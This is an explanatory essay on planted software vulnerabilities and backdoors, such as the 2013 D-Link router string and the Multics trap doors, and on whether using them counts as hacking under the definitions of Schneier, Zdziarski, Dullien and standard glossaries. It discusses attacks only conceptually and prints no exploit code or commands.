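# Deliberately planted vulnerabilities and whether exploiting them counts as hacking

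## What a planted vulnerability is

A planted vulnerability is a security flaw that someone put into a computer system on purpose. The person responsible may be acting for the company that designed the system, or may be a single employee or an outsider who gained influence over how others build it. People disagree about whether using such a flaw counts as hacking. Hacking usually means making a system do something its security was supposed to prevent. A planted flaw lets someone do that, but the system is also doing what somebody built it to do.

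In a simple case from October 2013, security researcher Craig Heffner read through the built-in software of a D-Link home router and found a way around the owner's password. Web browsers send a User-Agent string with each request, a short line of text that identifies the browser to the server. According to CERT Coordination Center's *D-Link routers authenticate administrative access using specific User-Agent string* (2013), a notice from a US body that collects reports of software flaws, the router's web server skipped the login check if that line contained one particular string of thirty characters. A US government alert the next day, CISA's *Reports of D-Link Router Backdoor* (2013), warned that a remote user could do anything an administrator could without logging in.

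Eight D-Link models had the flaw, and probably three from another brand, Planex. D-Link had turned off web configuration from the internet by default, which kept most outsiders out unless they could reach the home network some other way. However, the CERT Coordination Center saw some evidence that at least one internet provider had supplied routers with remote management turned on. According to NIST, the US standards agency that keeps the national vulnerability database, attackers were exploiting the flaw that same October. D-Link released a patch on 28 November.

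The string was deliberate. According to Tom's Hardware's *Some D-Link Routers Have Backdoor Vulnerability*, it spells "edit by joel backdoor" when read backwards without its digits. Joel's reasons are less clear. Building on a suggestion from another researcher, Travis Goodspeed, Heffner guessed in Krebs on Security that some of the router's own programs needed to change its settings automatically. The web server already had the code to do this, but it required a username and password, which the owner could change at any time. A phrase that always worked would have solved that problem. Krebs on Security hedged by calling the backdoor "a feature or bug".

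Sending that string to someone's router gets the sender past a password that the owner set to keep people out, which sounds like hacking. But the router is doing what somebody programmed it to do, which is to compare the browser's text with a stored phrase and open the settings if they match.

### The parts of a backdoor

A vulnerability is a property of a system that lets someone do what its security was supposed to prevent. An exploit is the input or series of actions that uses it. In the D-Link router, the vulnerability is the comparison inside the web server, and the exploit is a request that carries the string. The word "vulnerability" ordinarily covers planted flaws as well as mistakes. CERT, for example, published its warning as a "vulnerability note" and called the flaw a backdoor in the first paragraph. Some writers reserve the word for mistakes, but the wider sense is more practical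 because people usually find a flaw well before they know who put it there, or why.

The planter of a vulnerability is the person or organization that deliberately puts it in a system. A backdoor is a planted vulnerability that the planter hides from the system's users and that gives access to those who know about it. Someone who builds vulnerabilities into a practice system and tells the students they are there has not made a backdoor.

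A login page shows how a backdoor works. An honest one takes whatever the visitor types, checks it against the stored password, and lets the visitor in or refuses. Now suppose that the programmer adds one condition, so that the page lets the visitor in if the typed text equals a certain fixed phrase *or* if it is the right password. The example comes from two security researchers, Thomas and Francillon, in *Backdoors*, who in 2018 tried to give the word a rigorous meaning. They divide every backdoor into four parts:

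- The input source is the place the text comes from, here the login box.
- The trigger is the condition that activates the backdoor: the typed text equals the fixed phrase.
- The payload is whatever the program does next to get the visitor to the access. Here that is a single jump past the real password check.
- The privileged state is where the visitor ends up, logged in.

The backdoor stops working if any one of these four parts is missing, so they argue that the four are a minimum. Each part can be more elaborate. The input source might be the system clock, so that the backdoor opens only between certain dates. In a second example, the trigger is a special username, and the payload marks the visitor as an administrator and then opens a command line hidden from ordinary users. In a third, the program runs whatever instructions arrive with the trigger, so the planter doesn't have to decide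 in advance what the backdoor is for.

The D-Link flaw is simple. If the User-Agent text in a network request matches a fixed string, the server treats the sender as the legitimate user. Thomas and Francillon analyzed eleven real backdoors, including this one, and note that most documented cases are about as simple, triggered by a fixed piece of text such as a hard-coded password.

A planter who wants a better disguise can write a bugdoor, a backdoor made to look like an ordinary programming mistake. Thomas and Francillon sketch a login routine that copies the username and password into a space with room for 80 characters and never checks that they fit. Text that is too long overwrites neighbouring memory (a buffer overflow), and carefully chosen text can divert the program to code it should never run. The code is the same whether the programmer forgot the length check, which would be a mistake,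 or left it out on purpose, which would make it a backdoor. Thomas and Francillon also describe a hybrid, in which one special username leads to the faulty routine and every other username to a sound one. The hybrid keeps casual users away from the flaw, but an analyst can find the special username in the program, and it is hard to explain as a mistake.

### Four views of one system

Thomas and Francillon define a backdoor as an intentional construct that compromises a system's expected security by making otherwise privileged functions or information easier to reach. The person who intended the construct and the person who expected the security had different pictures of the system, so the paper describes each system in four ways: as the developer intended it, as it actually is, as the user expects it to be, and as an analyst recovers it by reverse-engineering the program.

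Each description is a finite state machine, a standard way of modelling a program as a set of states and the moves between them. The machine is written θ = (S, i, F, Σ, δ), where S is the set of states, i is the starting state, F is the set of states in which the program can finish, and Σ is the set of conditions that cause a move. The rule δ determines the next state from the current state and a condition.

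For the login page, the user's machine has three states, which can go by the names *check*, *in* and *out*. It starts at *check*, and its rule has two lines:

- δ(*check*, right password) = *in*
- δ(*check*, wrong password) = *out*

The machine that the programmer really built starts one step earlier, in a state called *compare*, and has two further lines:

- δ(*compare*, fixed phrase) = *in*
- δ(*compare*, anything else) = *check*

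The only differences are those two lines and the extra state. A user who never types the phrase passes through *compare* at every login without noticing it, so normal use will never reveal it.

| View | Whose picture it is | Ways to get in | Contains the backdoor? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Developer's | The person who wrote the code | Right password, fixed phrase | Yes |
| Actual | Nobody's: the program as it runs | Right password, fixed phrase | Yes |
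| Expected | The user | Right password | No |
| Reverse-engineered | An analyst studying the program | Right password, then also the phrase | Only once the analyst finds it |

On this account, a backdoor is in the developer's view and in the actual system, but not in what the user expects. With a bugdoor, the developer's view may include only part of it, because the planter leaves an opening without necessarily deciding how it will be used. An honest mistake is in the actual system but in neither the developer's view nor the user's. An administrator's login described in the manual is in all four.

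Under this definition, a backdoor can stop being one without any change to the router's code, which is a little odd. If D-Link had printed the thirty characters in the manual, owners who read it would have expected the second way in, so it would no longer have been a backdoor. It would still have been a planted vulnerability, because anybody on the network could still have used it to get past the password.

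The table also oversimplifies by giving "the user" and "the developer" one view each. Thomas and Francillon grant that different users have different expectations. A repair technician who has learned the phrase expects it to work, while the family that bought the router has never heard of it. Developers differ too, because a programmer can know of a line of code that the company's managers have never seen. When a flaw looks like a bug, no one can tell from the code whether it was intentional, which is why the paper sorts its cases into intentional backdoors, deniable ones and accidents.

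An older definition, which Thomas and Francillon quote from a 2000 paper by Zhang and Paxson, does not refer to expectations. It defines a backdoor as a mechanism that someone secretly adds to a system to make "unauthorised access" easier. Thomas and Francillon find this close to common usage but too general, because it leaves out what such a mechanism consists of. It does raise the question of who could have authorised the access, which their own definition does not address.

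### The people involved

With a planted flaw several people act, or fail to, and a verdict on one of them need not carry over to the next.

The planter is whoever puts the flaw in, whether or not anyone ever uses it. Nobody has publicly established who planted the one in the D-Link router. The CERT Coordination Center thought a manufacturer called Alpha Networks might have built the devices for both brands, but could not tell where in the supply chain the string was added.

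The planter may intend the flaw for their own repair staff or for an intelligence service. In the D-Link case, if Heffner's guess is right, it was meant only for other programs inside the same router.

A stranger may find a planted flaw that was not meant for him. Heffner did, and he published what he found so that others could do something about it. The attackers of October 2013 were also strangers, and they used the same string.

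The last party is the owner, who set a password and believed it was the only way in. An owner who forgot the password and sent the string to his own router would seem to have wronged no one. The thirty-character exploit alone therefore doesn't determine what kind of act someone has committed.

The D-Link case doesn't show who planted the vulnerability or why, but a much older case shows both. In 1972 and 1973 Paul Karger and Roger Schell, two US Air Force officers, tested the security of Multics, an operating system that many people could use at the same time. The Air Force was considering it for a Pentagon computer centre that would handle secret and top secret material side by side. In *Multics Security Evaluation*, Karger and Schell (1974) called a planted entrance a "trap door" and explained why an intruder would want one. Maintenance staff may at any time find and correct the existing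 mistakes an intruder relies on, and the intruder must then look for new ones. One trap door they described, which resembles the D-Link string of thirty-nine years later, sits in the code that handles typing. Ordinary typing has no effect on it, but a special sequence of keys gives unlimited access.

Karger and Schell also built a trap door. It sat in the most privileged part of Multics, in a routine that other programs called for an unrelated purpose, and it checked the 72 bits directly after one of the routine's normal inputs. If these matched a preset password, the routine copied a word of memory from one address to another with full privileges, which let the caller read or change anything in the core of the system. The password kept users from setting off the trap door by accident, since random bits would match it only about once in 4.7 × 10²¹ tries. Karger and Schell said the trap door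 took 18 hours of work and 80 dollars of computer time.

They briefed Honeywell, the manufacturer, in the spring of 1973, and Honeywell recompiled the routine so that the trap door would not reach other sites. But there was a second trap door in the software for Honeywell's next machine, and Karger and Schell (2002) report in *Thirty Years Later* that Honeywell delivered it to the Pentagon. It was harmless as it stood, but changing one instruction would have made it dangerous. Although the 1974 report contained a hint about it, it went unnoticed for roughly another year, until it returned an odd error during a security audit at General Motors, which also ran Multics.

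Here the planters were officers on an official project, playing the part of foreign agents, and the strangers were auditors at a car company. Whether the officers had permission is less clear. Karger and Schell tried out their break-ins on an Air Force machine before using them on the one at MIT, because a crash at MIT would have revealed what they were doing. This suggests that whoever ran the MIT machine had not agreed to the break-ins, or at least did not know the details. Karger and Schell thought intention was the main difference between malicious software and an "Easter egg", a joke that a programmer hides in a product. Most Easter eggs also require a secret key, and the programmer's managers never approved most of them.

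There are three main views on whether exploiting a planted vulnerability is hacking. The first is that using an entrance the designers intended is not hacking. This fits the security writer Bruce Schneier's definition of a hack as something a system allows but its designers neither intended nor anticipated. The second is that it is hacking to get in by a route that the people relying on the system did not know existed, whatever the planter intended. The third is that a person hacks a computer by using it without permission from someone entitled to give it, however the vulnerability got there.

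## The view that a flaw its designers intended is not hacked

The definition behind the first view comes from Schneier's *The Coming AI Hackers* (2021), an essay that treats tax law and sport as hackable, like computers. In the first part of the definition, a hack is a "clever, unintended exploitation of a system" that subverts the system's rules or norms at the expense of some other part of the system. In the second, a hack is something that a system allows but that is "unintended and unanticipated by its designers".

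One of Schneier's examples is the theft of personal data from the credit bureau Equifax in 2017. In his account, the Chinese military got in through a flaw in the web software Apache Struts, found passwords that opened other parts of the network, and downloaded information about 147 million people over four months. The software allowed all of this, although its designers didn't intend it to. Schneier also calls the curved hockey stick a hack. It made shots faster and the game more dangerous, and the rules didn't forbid it because nobody had thought of it.

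Since every hack is something the system allows, the rules alone can't separate a hack from ordinary use. Suppose two taxpayers fill in their returns correctly and each save 1,000 dollars. One uses a deduction that Congress created for people like her, and the other uses a gap between two clauses that nobody had noticed. Only the second taxpayer is a hacker, because Congress intended the deduction but not the gap. Schneier's definition requires a hack to be both unintended and unanticipated. Designers sometimes know that people will misuse a feature and keep it anyway, and under his definition that misuse isn't a hack.

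Schneier's *A Hacker's Mind* (2023), the book that grew out of the essay, changes the wording slightly. *A Hacker's Mind (Book Review)* quotes a passage in which the loser is now "someone else affected by the system". Another review, *How to Know if You're a Hacker, and Other Life Hacks*, quotes a shorter version in which a hack subverts "the goal or intent of the system". Introducing the book in *The Big Idea*, Schneier replaced "unintended" with "unwanted" and added that a hack is "a mistake in the system's design or coding". Taken literally, that phrase rules out planted flaws. But he probably hadn't changed his mind, because he repeated the 2021 wording in an interview about the book, the Ash Center's *Hacking to Harm and Heal Democracy* (2023).

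### Provisions written for lobbyists

Schneier treats the tax code as a program that takes a person's finances for the year and calculates the tax owed. Like other programs, it has bugs. A typing error in the 2017 US tax law classed military death benefits as earned income, and bereaved families received surprise bills of $10,000 or more. Schneier calls this error a bug but not a vulnerability, because nobody could use it to pay less tax.

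He does count the tax scheme known as the Double Irish with a Dutch Sandwich as a vulnerability. Companies such as Google and Apple used Irish and Dutch subsidiaries to move profits to places with little or no tax. No legislature had planned this route, which depended on how the laws of three countries fitted together. *Legal Zero-Days* (2025), a paper on flaws of this kind as a risk from advanced AI, gives an example from outside tax law. Australia's constitution has barred dual citizens from parliament since 1901. In 2017 it emerged that this rule, combined with other countries' citizenship laws, disqualified sitting members, and the deputy prime minister had to resign.

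Other vulnerabilities are deliberate. Schneier writes that lobbyists constantly try to get provisions into the tax code for their clients, and he gives three examples from the same 2017 law: a special tax break for oil and gas investment partnerships, an exemption that leaves fewer than one estate in a thousand paying estate tax, and wording that expanded a loophole companies use to incorporate offshore. The estate tax exemption is a weaker example than the others, because an exemption that broad is hard to hide and the legislators who voted for it may simply have wanted it.

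He compares these provisions to the backdoors that programmers add to software for their own purposes. He argues that the lobbyist has hacked the legislative process and the programmer has hacked the software development process, but neither has hacked the code itself. This fits his definition well enough, because the procedure for amending a bill allows a member to add a paragraph for a lobbyist's client, even though its purpose is to produce laws that the members have considered.

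Schneier isn't entirely consistent about this. Later in the essay he says "Some hacks are written into the law", which suggests that the provision itself is the hack. He may only mean that a trick can gain legal standing over time, as he thinks the filibuster did in the US Senate.

### From inserting a flaw to using it

Schneier's passage on lobbyists is about the person who inserts a flaw. He doesn't say in the essay whether the oil partnership that later claims the tax break is hacking, or whether the stranger who types a backdoor's password is. He doesn't address the question in the Ash Center interview or in his own summary of *A Hacker's Mind* either. The view that using a planted flaw is not a hack is an inference from his definition of a hack as a use that the designers neither intended nor anticipated. Whoever planted the flaw was one of the designers and intended people to use it.

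Even if the inference works, it covers fewer people than it first seems to. The definition's test is whether the designers intended the *use*, and someone who plants a flaw usually has particular users in mind. If Heffner guessed right about the D-Link router, the programmer meant the secret string for the router's own software. The attackers of October 2013 used it for something else, which the programmer presumably had not intended.

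It is harder to say whether he anticipated break-ins. Someone who puts the word "backdoor" in a password must have some idea that an outsider could find it. If he did foresee break-ins, they were unintended but not unanticipated, so they were not hacks under Schneier's wording, which requires both. It would be strange if the attackers weren't hacking because the programmer had been reckless. The definition would work better here if it required only that a use be unintended.

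### Loopholes people buy and loopholes people find

The view is most persuasive as a way of deciding what to do about a flaw. When someone discovers a loophole by accident, rule-makers usually want to close it. For example, the 2017 US tax law capped the deduction for property taxes from 2018 onwards, and some taxpayers saw that they could avoid the cap by paying their 2018 property tax early. Just before the end of 2017, the US tax authority ruled that this was not legal in most cases.

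Pointing out a loophole does much less good when powerful people want it there. Schneier (2026) writes in *Entries Tagged "laws"*, a collection of his blog posts, that several administrations have tried to close the carried interest loophole, a decades-old US tax dodge, but lobbyists have persuaded legislators to keep it. He doesn't say that anyone planted it, but a provision that a lobbyist did plant would have the same protection from the start, because the legislators who could repeal it include those who put it there.

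Planted provisions therefore call for changes to the way legislatures work, much as a planted backdoor in software calls for more than a patch, which doesn't remove the employee who wrote it. In *How AI Could Write Our Laws* (2023), Schneier and the data scientist Nathan Sanders propose that legislatures rely less on bills of several thousand pages that members must pass by a deadline, and that they leave more time between an amendment and the vote. They would also have lobbyists publish, within a few days of a meeting, what they asked for and why. These changes would have done little about the Double Irish, which didn't need a lobbyist to insert it.

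The view also assigns blame sensibly. An heir who claims an exemption that Congress deliberately passed is using the law as intended. Anyone who objects to the exemption should hold Congress and the lobbyists responsible, and calling the heir a hacker would distract from their role.

One can object to this view by drawing the boundary of "the system" more widely. *Bruce Schneier's A Hacker's Mind* (2023), a review on Cory Doctorow's blog Pluralistic, distinguishes lobbying for a loophole from discovering an accidental one, but counts both as ways to hack the tax system, along with corrupting tax inspectors. If the tax system includes the legislature, lobbying for a loophole and then using it look like two stages of one hack.

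Schneier himself draws a wide boundary when he discusses Volkswagen. The company's engineers programmed its cars to recognize an emissions test and to switch on the full pollution controls only during the test. On the road, the cars emitted up to forty times the permitted amount of nitrogen oxides. The engineers designed the software to do this, yet Schneier calls it a hack, presumably because they subverted the test, which regulators had designed. So a designer's intent doesn't settle whether something is a hack. One also has to know which system is in question and who designed it.

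### Designers who did not know

Schneier notes that the legislator who sponsors an amendment doesn't always know about the vulnerability in it. The other legislators may know even less. He writes that Congress drafted the 2017 tax law in haste and in secret, with parts handwritten, and he thinks it "pretty much inconceivable" that anyone who voted on it knew precisely what was in it. This is a problem for the inference, which depends on the planter being a designer whose intention counts. A lobbyist may have intended a tax break that the sponsor and most other legislators never noticed.

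Legislators can also know what a provision says without understanding its purpose. Sanders and Schneier describe a 2013 Massachusetts bill that would have restricted commercial use of schoolchildren's data. The bill appealed to people who cared about privacy, but its sponsor had introduced it at the request of Microsoft's lobbyists, who wanted to keep Google Docs out of classrooms. If it had passed, some of its designers would have intended to protect children and others to shut out a competitor.

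Schneier could reply that the author's intention is what counts. The lobbyist who wrote the tax break would then be its designer, and a client who claimed it would not be hacking. This rule is simple, but it makes anyone who gets a line into the text a designer. A criminal who broke into a software company and added a backdoor to its product would become one of the product's designers, and a second criminal who bought the password from him would not be hacking when he used it.

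One could also reply that Congress acts as a body and intends every line of a bill it passes. Courts and tax offices do have to apply the whole text, regardless of what the members read. But if a vote were enough to make every line intentional, Congress would also have intended the typing error it passed about death benefits, and it would be hard to see how a statute could contain a mistake.

He could instead rely on the wording that a hack subverts the goal of the system, and say that individual legislators' knowledge doesn't matter much. A tax code exists to raise revenue by general rules, and a secret exception for one industry works against that. But then using the exception is a hack even if whoever planted it intended that use, which the first view denies. People also disagree about the goal. Some who voted for the 2017 law may have thought its purpose was to let businesses keep more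 of their money.

The most workable reply is probably to count only the intentions of people entitled to decide what the system does, and to ask what they knew at the time. If the bill's sponsor and the other legislators did not know that it contained a tax break, using the tax break is a hack, at least at first. If they find out and leave it alone for years, they have accepted it and its use becomes normal. This fits Schneier's account of how rules develop, in which courts and governing bodies look at a new hack and either forbid it or absorb it. An odd consequence is that a company could file the same tax return every year, and at some point doing so would no longer be a hack.

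This reply gives up the general claim that nobody can hack a planted flaw. Using the flaw is not hacking if the people in charge wanted it there, but it can be if the planter acted without their knowledge. The reply also depends on knowing who was entitled to decide, which is close to asking who could give permission.

### Provisions drafted with AI

Much of Schneier's later work with Sanders is about how AI could help people write provisions that legislators won't notice. They borrow the word "microlegislation" from the political scientist Amy McKay, who uses it for small pieces of proposed law that serve narrow interests. McKay studied the 564 amendments to the Affordable Care Act that a US Senate committee considered in 2009, along with the positions and campaign contributions of 866 lobbying groups. Some lobbyists' comments went directly into amendments. Contributions to particular senators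 on the committee made the amendments more likely to pass.

Sanders and Schneier then describe how a lobbyist might automate this. A language model trained on past bills and amendments would propose small changes to a text and predict whether a human reader would recognize each change as important. An economic model would estimate what each change was worth to the client. Another program, trained on the connections between legislators, donors and interest groups, would work out whom to persuade and how. Sanders and Schneier thought in 2023 that the necessary techniques existed but that lobbyists' use of them was still hypothetical.

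The prediction about readers matters most for the definition of a hack. A lobbyist who used it would be choosing provisions because legislators were unlikely to anticipate them. The client would intend the effect and almost nobody else would know of it, so the question of whose intention counts could come up in many bills. Sanders and Schneier call the strategy a hack, in line with the 2021 essay. They also write that very large bills are "ripe for hacking by microlegislation", which suggests that the lobbyist hacks the bill as well as the process.

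AI could also produce a loophole that no person planned. Sanders and Schneier (2025), in *AI Will Write Complex Laws*, report that a Brazilian municipality passed a law in 2023 without its legislators knowing that ChatGPT had written it, though they don't suggest it contained a loophole. If a model drafted a clause that happened to favour one company, and neither the person who asked for the draft nor the legislators noticed, the clause would be an accident. The company would be hacking, in Schneier's sense, if it later found and used the clause. If the model's developer had trained it to favour that company, the same clause would be a planted flaw, but legislators couldn't tell this from the text.

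Schneier suggested in 2021 that a watchdog or a journalist could use AI to search a bill for loopholes before the vote. One of his 2026 posts quotes researchers who used language models to find a substantial number of vulnerabilities in existing German law that, as far as they knew, no one had recorded before. If someone published a list of a bill's loopholes and legislators passed the bill unchanged, they could no longer say that they hadn't anticipated them. Under Schneier's definition, a company that then used one of the loopholes would not be hacking, whether or not a lobbyist had planted it.

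## The view that the user's expectations decide

The second view defines a system's security by what its users have been led to expect. The maker of a router tells buyers, in the manual or just by putting a password box on the screen, that the password keeps strangers out. On this view, anyone who gets in by a method the owner never heard of has broken the router's security, even if the maker built that method in and wanted people to use it.

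Many security writers assume something like this without arguing for it. The security researcher Jonathan Zdziarski spelled it out in *Backdoor* (2016) because he wanted a definition of the word that courts and legislators could use. In February 2016 the FBI had asked for a court order to make Apple help it bypass the security of Apple's own software. In the hearings that followed, both sides talked about backdoors without agreeing on what the word meant.

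### Zdziarski's three questions

Zdziarski has three questions about any component of a security mechanism. It is a backdoor only if the answer to all three is yes.

- Intent: does it work against the purposes that the maker disclosed to the computer's owner?
- Consent: is it active without the owner's consent?
- Access: is it under the control of someone the owner hasn't been told about?

"Owner" here means whoever is entitled to control access to the computer, so the owner of an office laptop is usually the employer.

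The first two answers depend on what Zdziarski calls the user contract, the shared understanding between maker and user of what a mechanism is for. It needn't be a legal document. The maker sets the terms by describing the product, and the user accepts them by switching it on. If the maker later wants the mechanism to do something else, it has to tell the user first. For example, an update that adds a licensing component users might dislike breaks the contract unless the maker discloses it beforehand, perhaps in the release notes.

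Zdziarski applies this to a router with a built-in maintenance password that works no matter what password the owner sets. The owner understood that the login would admit only people whose passwords an administrator had created, so the maintenance password works against the disclosed purpose. The owner didn't consent to it, because they didn't know about it and can't turn it off. Anyone who has the password can get past the login, even if the owner has never heard of them. The router therefore has a backdoor, even if the manufacturer only wanted to make repairs cheaper.

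A software-update service is a harder case, because it lets an outsider change the owner's computer more thoroughly than many backdoors do. But the maker has told the owner that updates fix bugs and add features, and the owner has turned them on. The service isn't a backdoor as long as it installs only the kind of code the maker described.

Suppose the government secretly orders the maker to send spyware through the same service. Zdziarski would then call the service a backdoor, even if it runs exactly as before. It works against its disclosed purpose, which cancels the owner's consent, and the government controls it without the owner's knowledge. If criminals instead break into the service and send out malware, he calls it a compromised mechanism, not a backdoor, because the maker's intentions haven't changed.

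So the maker's intentions still matter in Zdziarski's test, and they made one of his own cases difficult. File Relay was an Apple service that ran on millions of iPhones and other devices without their users' knowledge. Anyone with the unlocked device or a pairing record from the user's computer could use it to get the device's data without the encryption that the user's backup password was supposed to provide. Apple said the service was for diagnostics. Companies that made forensic tools for the police built it into their products. Zdziarski thought File Relay met his conditions on consent and access, but he left intent open because Apple might have bypassed its own encryption by mistake.

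Someone who thinks the user's expectations alone decide whether exploiting a planted vulnerability counts as hacking would have to go further than Zdziarski. The users had set a password to protect their backups, and the police tools got around it, whether or not Apple had meant to allow that.

His test also classifies mechanisms, not the people who use them, so applying it to hacking requires an inference, as it did with Schneier. If a system's security is what its maker led the owner to expect, then anyone who uses a backdoor, including the manufacturer's own technician, would be defeating that security, which is what people ordinarily mean by hacking.

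### Weird states

In *Weird machines, exploitability, and provable unexploitability*, the security researcher Thomas Dullien describes break-ins in terms of what happens inside the program rather than what the owner knew. He wanted to define precisely what professional exploit writers mean by "exploit".

Dullien treats a program as a stand-in for a machine that somebody had in mind. The intended machine is a finite state machine, like the one for the login page. It exists only as a design, so a programmer writes software that imitates it on a general-purpose processor. He argues that one can't define a software flaw without some idea of the flawless version.

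The processor can be in far more states than the intended machine has. Some represent a state of the intended machine, and others occur briefly during transitions between those states. Dullien calls the rest weird states. A program in a weird state usually keeps running and applies its normal steps to data that no longer makes sense. The attacker's inputs then work like instructions for a new computer that nobody designed, which Dullien calls a weird machine. For him, exploitation means getting the program into a weird state and then steering it so that it violates a security property of the intended machine.

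His example is a small program that stores up to 5,000 secrets, each with its own password, and hands over a secret to anyone who sends the right password. Passwords and secrets are 32-bit numbers. The security property is that an attacker can't do better than guessing. If the attacker sends *n* messages, then

P(attacker gets the secret) ≤ *n* / 2³²

For a single message, that is about one chance in 4.3 billion.

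Dullien then lets the attacker change one bit of the program's memory. In one version of the program, each entry contains a number that gives the location of the next entry. The attacker uses the one bit to make one of these numbers too large by one, so the program starts reading the next entry one position late and treats a secret as a password. The attacker planted that secret, so he can send it as a password. The program returns the value it reads as the matching secret and clears the entry, which overwrites another user's password with a number the attacker can work out. The attacker sends that number and receives the other user's secret.

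A second version keeps everything in a plain table without these location numbers. Dullien proves that the bit gives an attacker almost no advantage there, because an attacker without it could do as well by sending at most 10,000 extra messages.

A bugdoor fits this account well. In the login routine with the missing length check, overlong text puts the program in a state that its apparent design doesn't include, and the intruder takes control from there.

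An openly coded backdoor that checks for a fixed phrase doesn't fit Dullien's model of exploitation. The check is an ordinary line of the program, and the processor follows it when somebody types the phrase. Thomas and Francillon, whose four views of a system grew out of that model, likewise write that a traditional exploit reaches a weird state, whereas a backdoor is "essentially normal program functionality".

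Taken literally, Dullien's account would even support the first view. In slides from a 2011 talk, Dullien said that the programmer defines the valid states, so a programmer who adds a backdoor has defined a machine that accepts the backdoor phrase. Dullien also requires every security property to be a true statement about the intended machine, and "nobody gets in without the right password" is false of that machine. The attackers who sent the D-Link string in 2013 would therefore have violated no security property, and so would not have exploited anything.

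Using the machine that the user expects instead meets only part of Dullien's definition of exploitation. In the expected machine, nobody gets in without the right password, so the phrase violates a security property. But the program ends up in the ordinary logged-in state, which the expected machine also has. The expected machine lacks only the step from the phrase to that state. The program was therefore probably never in a weird state, which the definition also requires.

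### Whether the route matters

Skill is a poor guide to whether someone has broken in, though it gives some reason to reserve the word "hacking" for weird states. Programming a machine that nobody designed takes skill, while anyone can type a phrase from a website. But few people would say that the intruders at Equifax stopped hacking whenever they logged in to other parts of the network with passwords they had found, even though the software processed these as normal logins.

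If hacking were defined by weird states, whether the intruder had hacked the program would also depend on how the planter wrote the vulnerability. A planter could provide the same access with a secret phrase or with a missing length check, and only the second would make its user a hacker. In the hybrid version, where a special username leads to a faulty routine, the intruder would be using the program normally while typing the username and hacking it while typing the password. The owner is equally badly off in all three cases.

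Dullien's proof about the plain table suggests a better criterion. Some of the one-bit changes he considers take the program from one legitimate state to another by an unintended path. He dismisses these changes because they don't give the attacker a significant advantage, not because both states are legitimate. By that standard the fixed phrase is a serious breach, since a stranger who would otherwise have to guess gets in on the first try. It seems reasonable to keep Dullien's requirement that a security property be violated, judge the violation against what the user was led to expect, and drop the requirement of a weird state.

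The difference does matter to people looking for flaws. A common method is fuzzing, in which a tool feeds a program huge numbers of partly random inputs and watches for crashes. Kokkonis, Marcozzi and colleagues (2025) point out in *ROSA* that a well-written backdoor shouldn't crash anything, so ordinary fuzzing misses it. Their tool, also called ROSA, compares inputs that should have similar effects. For example, all wrong passwords should make a login program react in much the same way, so ROSA flags one that opens a command line.

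The researchers tested ROSA on 17 backdoors, seven of them authentic and ten they wrote themselves. It found all 17, in an hour and a half on average, while an older tool, Stringer, found four. A person still had to check an average of seven suspicious behaviours per backdoor. ROSA works from a crude version of what a user would expect, which is that similar inputs have similar results, and has no access to the programmer's intentions.

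### What the glossaries define

If the second view captured ordinary usage, standard definitions should refer to what users know, and definitions of "backdoor" mostly do. The main definition of *backdoor* in NIST's online glossary is "an undocumented way of gaining access" to a computer system, and it doesn't mention who made it or why. MITRE, a US non-profit organization that catalogues software weaknesses, has a related category called *Hidden Functionality* for functions that are undocumented, outside the specification and not reachable in any way obvious to users or administrators. The longer entry for *Hidden Functionality* in GCVE's public vulnerability database gives malicious code, Easter eggs and hard-coded accounts as examples, and adds that even harmless ones can give attackers more to exploit.

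Definitions agree less on whether a back door must be intentional. In *Internet Security Glossary, Version 2* (RFC 4949), Shirey (2007) allows it to be an unintentional flaw, a deliberate installation by the system's creator, or an intruder's addition. He requires only that it give access by an unusual procedure, and describes it as "usually" hidden or not well known. In 1994 Carl Landwehr and colleagues had divided security flaws into intentional and inadvertent ones, and Shirey's back doors can be either. Kokkonis and colleagues also include unintentional back doors, such as debugging access that a developer forgot to remove.

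The *Cyber Glossary* from the National Security Archive, a research institute in Washington, gives two US definitions of a backdoor. The first, from a government glossary for national security systems, describes a "typically unauthorized hidden" mechanism for getting around security controls. The second, from the Cyberspace Solarium Commission in 2020, describes an "intentionally designed vulnerability" that enables access. Unlike the first, this definition includes intention and leaves out secrecy and permission.

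Definitions of "hacker" differ. NIST defines a hacker as an "unauthorized user" who gains or tries to gain access to an information system. ATIS, a telecommunications standards body, lists five meanings. Three involve a lack of authorization, and one is a computer enthusiast. The fifth is someone who uses a computer in a way "for which it is not intended" or against an acceptable-use policy, which is fairly close to Schneier's idea of a hack. Shirey prefers the old meaning, someone who enjoys computers and is good at figuring them out, and blames journalists in particular for the criminal one. But he also lists penetrating a system as one meaning of the verb "to hack".

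| Definition | Intention | Secrecy | Permission |
|---|---|---|---|
| Zdziarski, backdoor | Works against disclosed purposes | Undisclosed | No consent from the owner |
| NIST, backdoor | Not mentioned | Undocumented | Not mentioned |
| Shirey, back door | Deliberate or accidental | Usually hidden | Not mentioned |
| National Security Archive, first definition | Not mentioned | Hidden | Typically unauthorized |
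| National Security Archive, second definition | Deliberate | Not mentioned | Not mentioned |
| MITRE, hidden functionality | Outside the specification | Undocumented and not obvious | Not mentioned |
| NIST, hacker | Not mentioned | Not mentioned | Unauthorized |
| ATIS, hacker, fifth meaning | Use not intended | Not mentioned | Against an acceptable-use policy |

The glossaries therefore support the second view only in part. They mostly define a backdoor by its secrecy and a hacker by lack of permission. Shirey mentions that manufacturers sometimes ship operating systems with hidden accounts for their field technicians. A technician who uses such an account on a job the customer requested has used a backdoor, but he isn't a hacker under NIST's definition.

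### Whose expectations count

One objection is that expectations are vague and differ from person to person. Most people who buy a router don't know how its login works. A security professional who has seen dozens of hard-coded passwords may half expect one in any cheap router. If an expectation were just a prediction, breaking into the professional's router would be less of a hack than breaking into his neighbour's, which is absurd.

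It makes more sense to ask what an owner is entitled to count on. Under Zdziarski's user contract, that depends on what the maker disclosed, which anyone can check by reading the manual. He applies this test strictly to the Clipper chip, an encryption chip that the US National Security Agency developed with a built-in way for law enforcement to decrypt messages. The public knew about this from the news, but the manual for the one product that used the chip, a telephone security device from AT&T, didn't mention it. Zdziarski concludes that the device had a backdoor, since press coverage isn't disclosure by the manufacturer. He concedes that a government employee who knew all about the chip might see the device as an internal surveillance device instead.

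The same rule gives a sensible answer about the D-Link router. After Heffner published the string, owners who read about it knew it would work. Thomas and Francillon's definition requires that the user not expect the backdoor, so by that definition those owners arguably no longer had one. For Zdziarski they still did, because a researcher's findings don't change what D-Link told its customers. NIST's word "undocumented" leaves the case unclear, because the CERT Coordination Center had documented the string in detail, but D-Link's customers were unlikely to look there.

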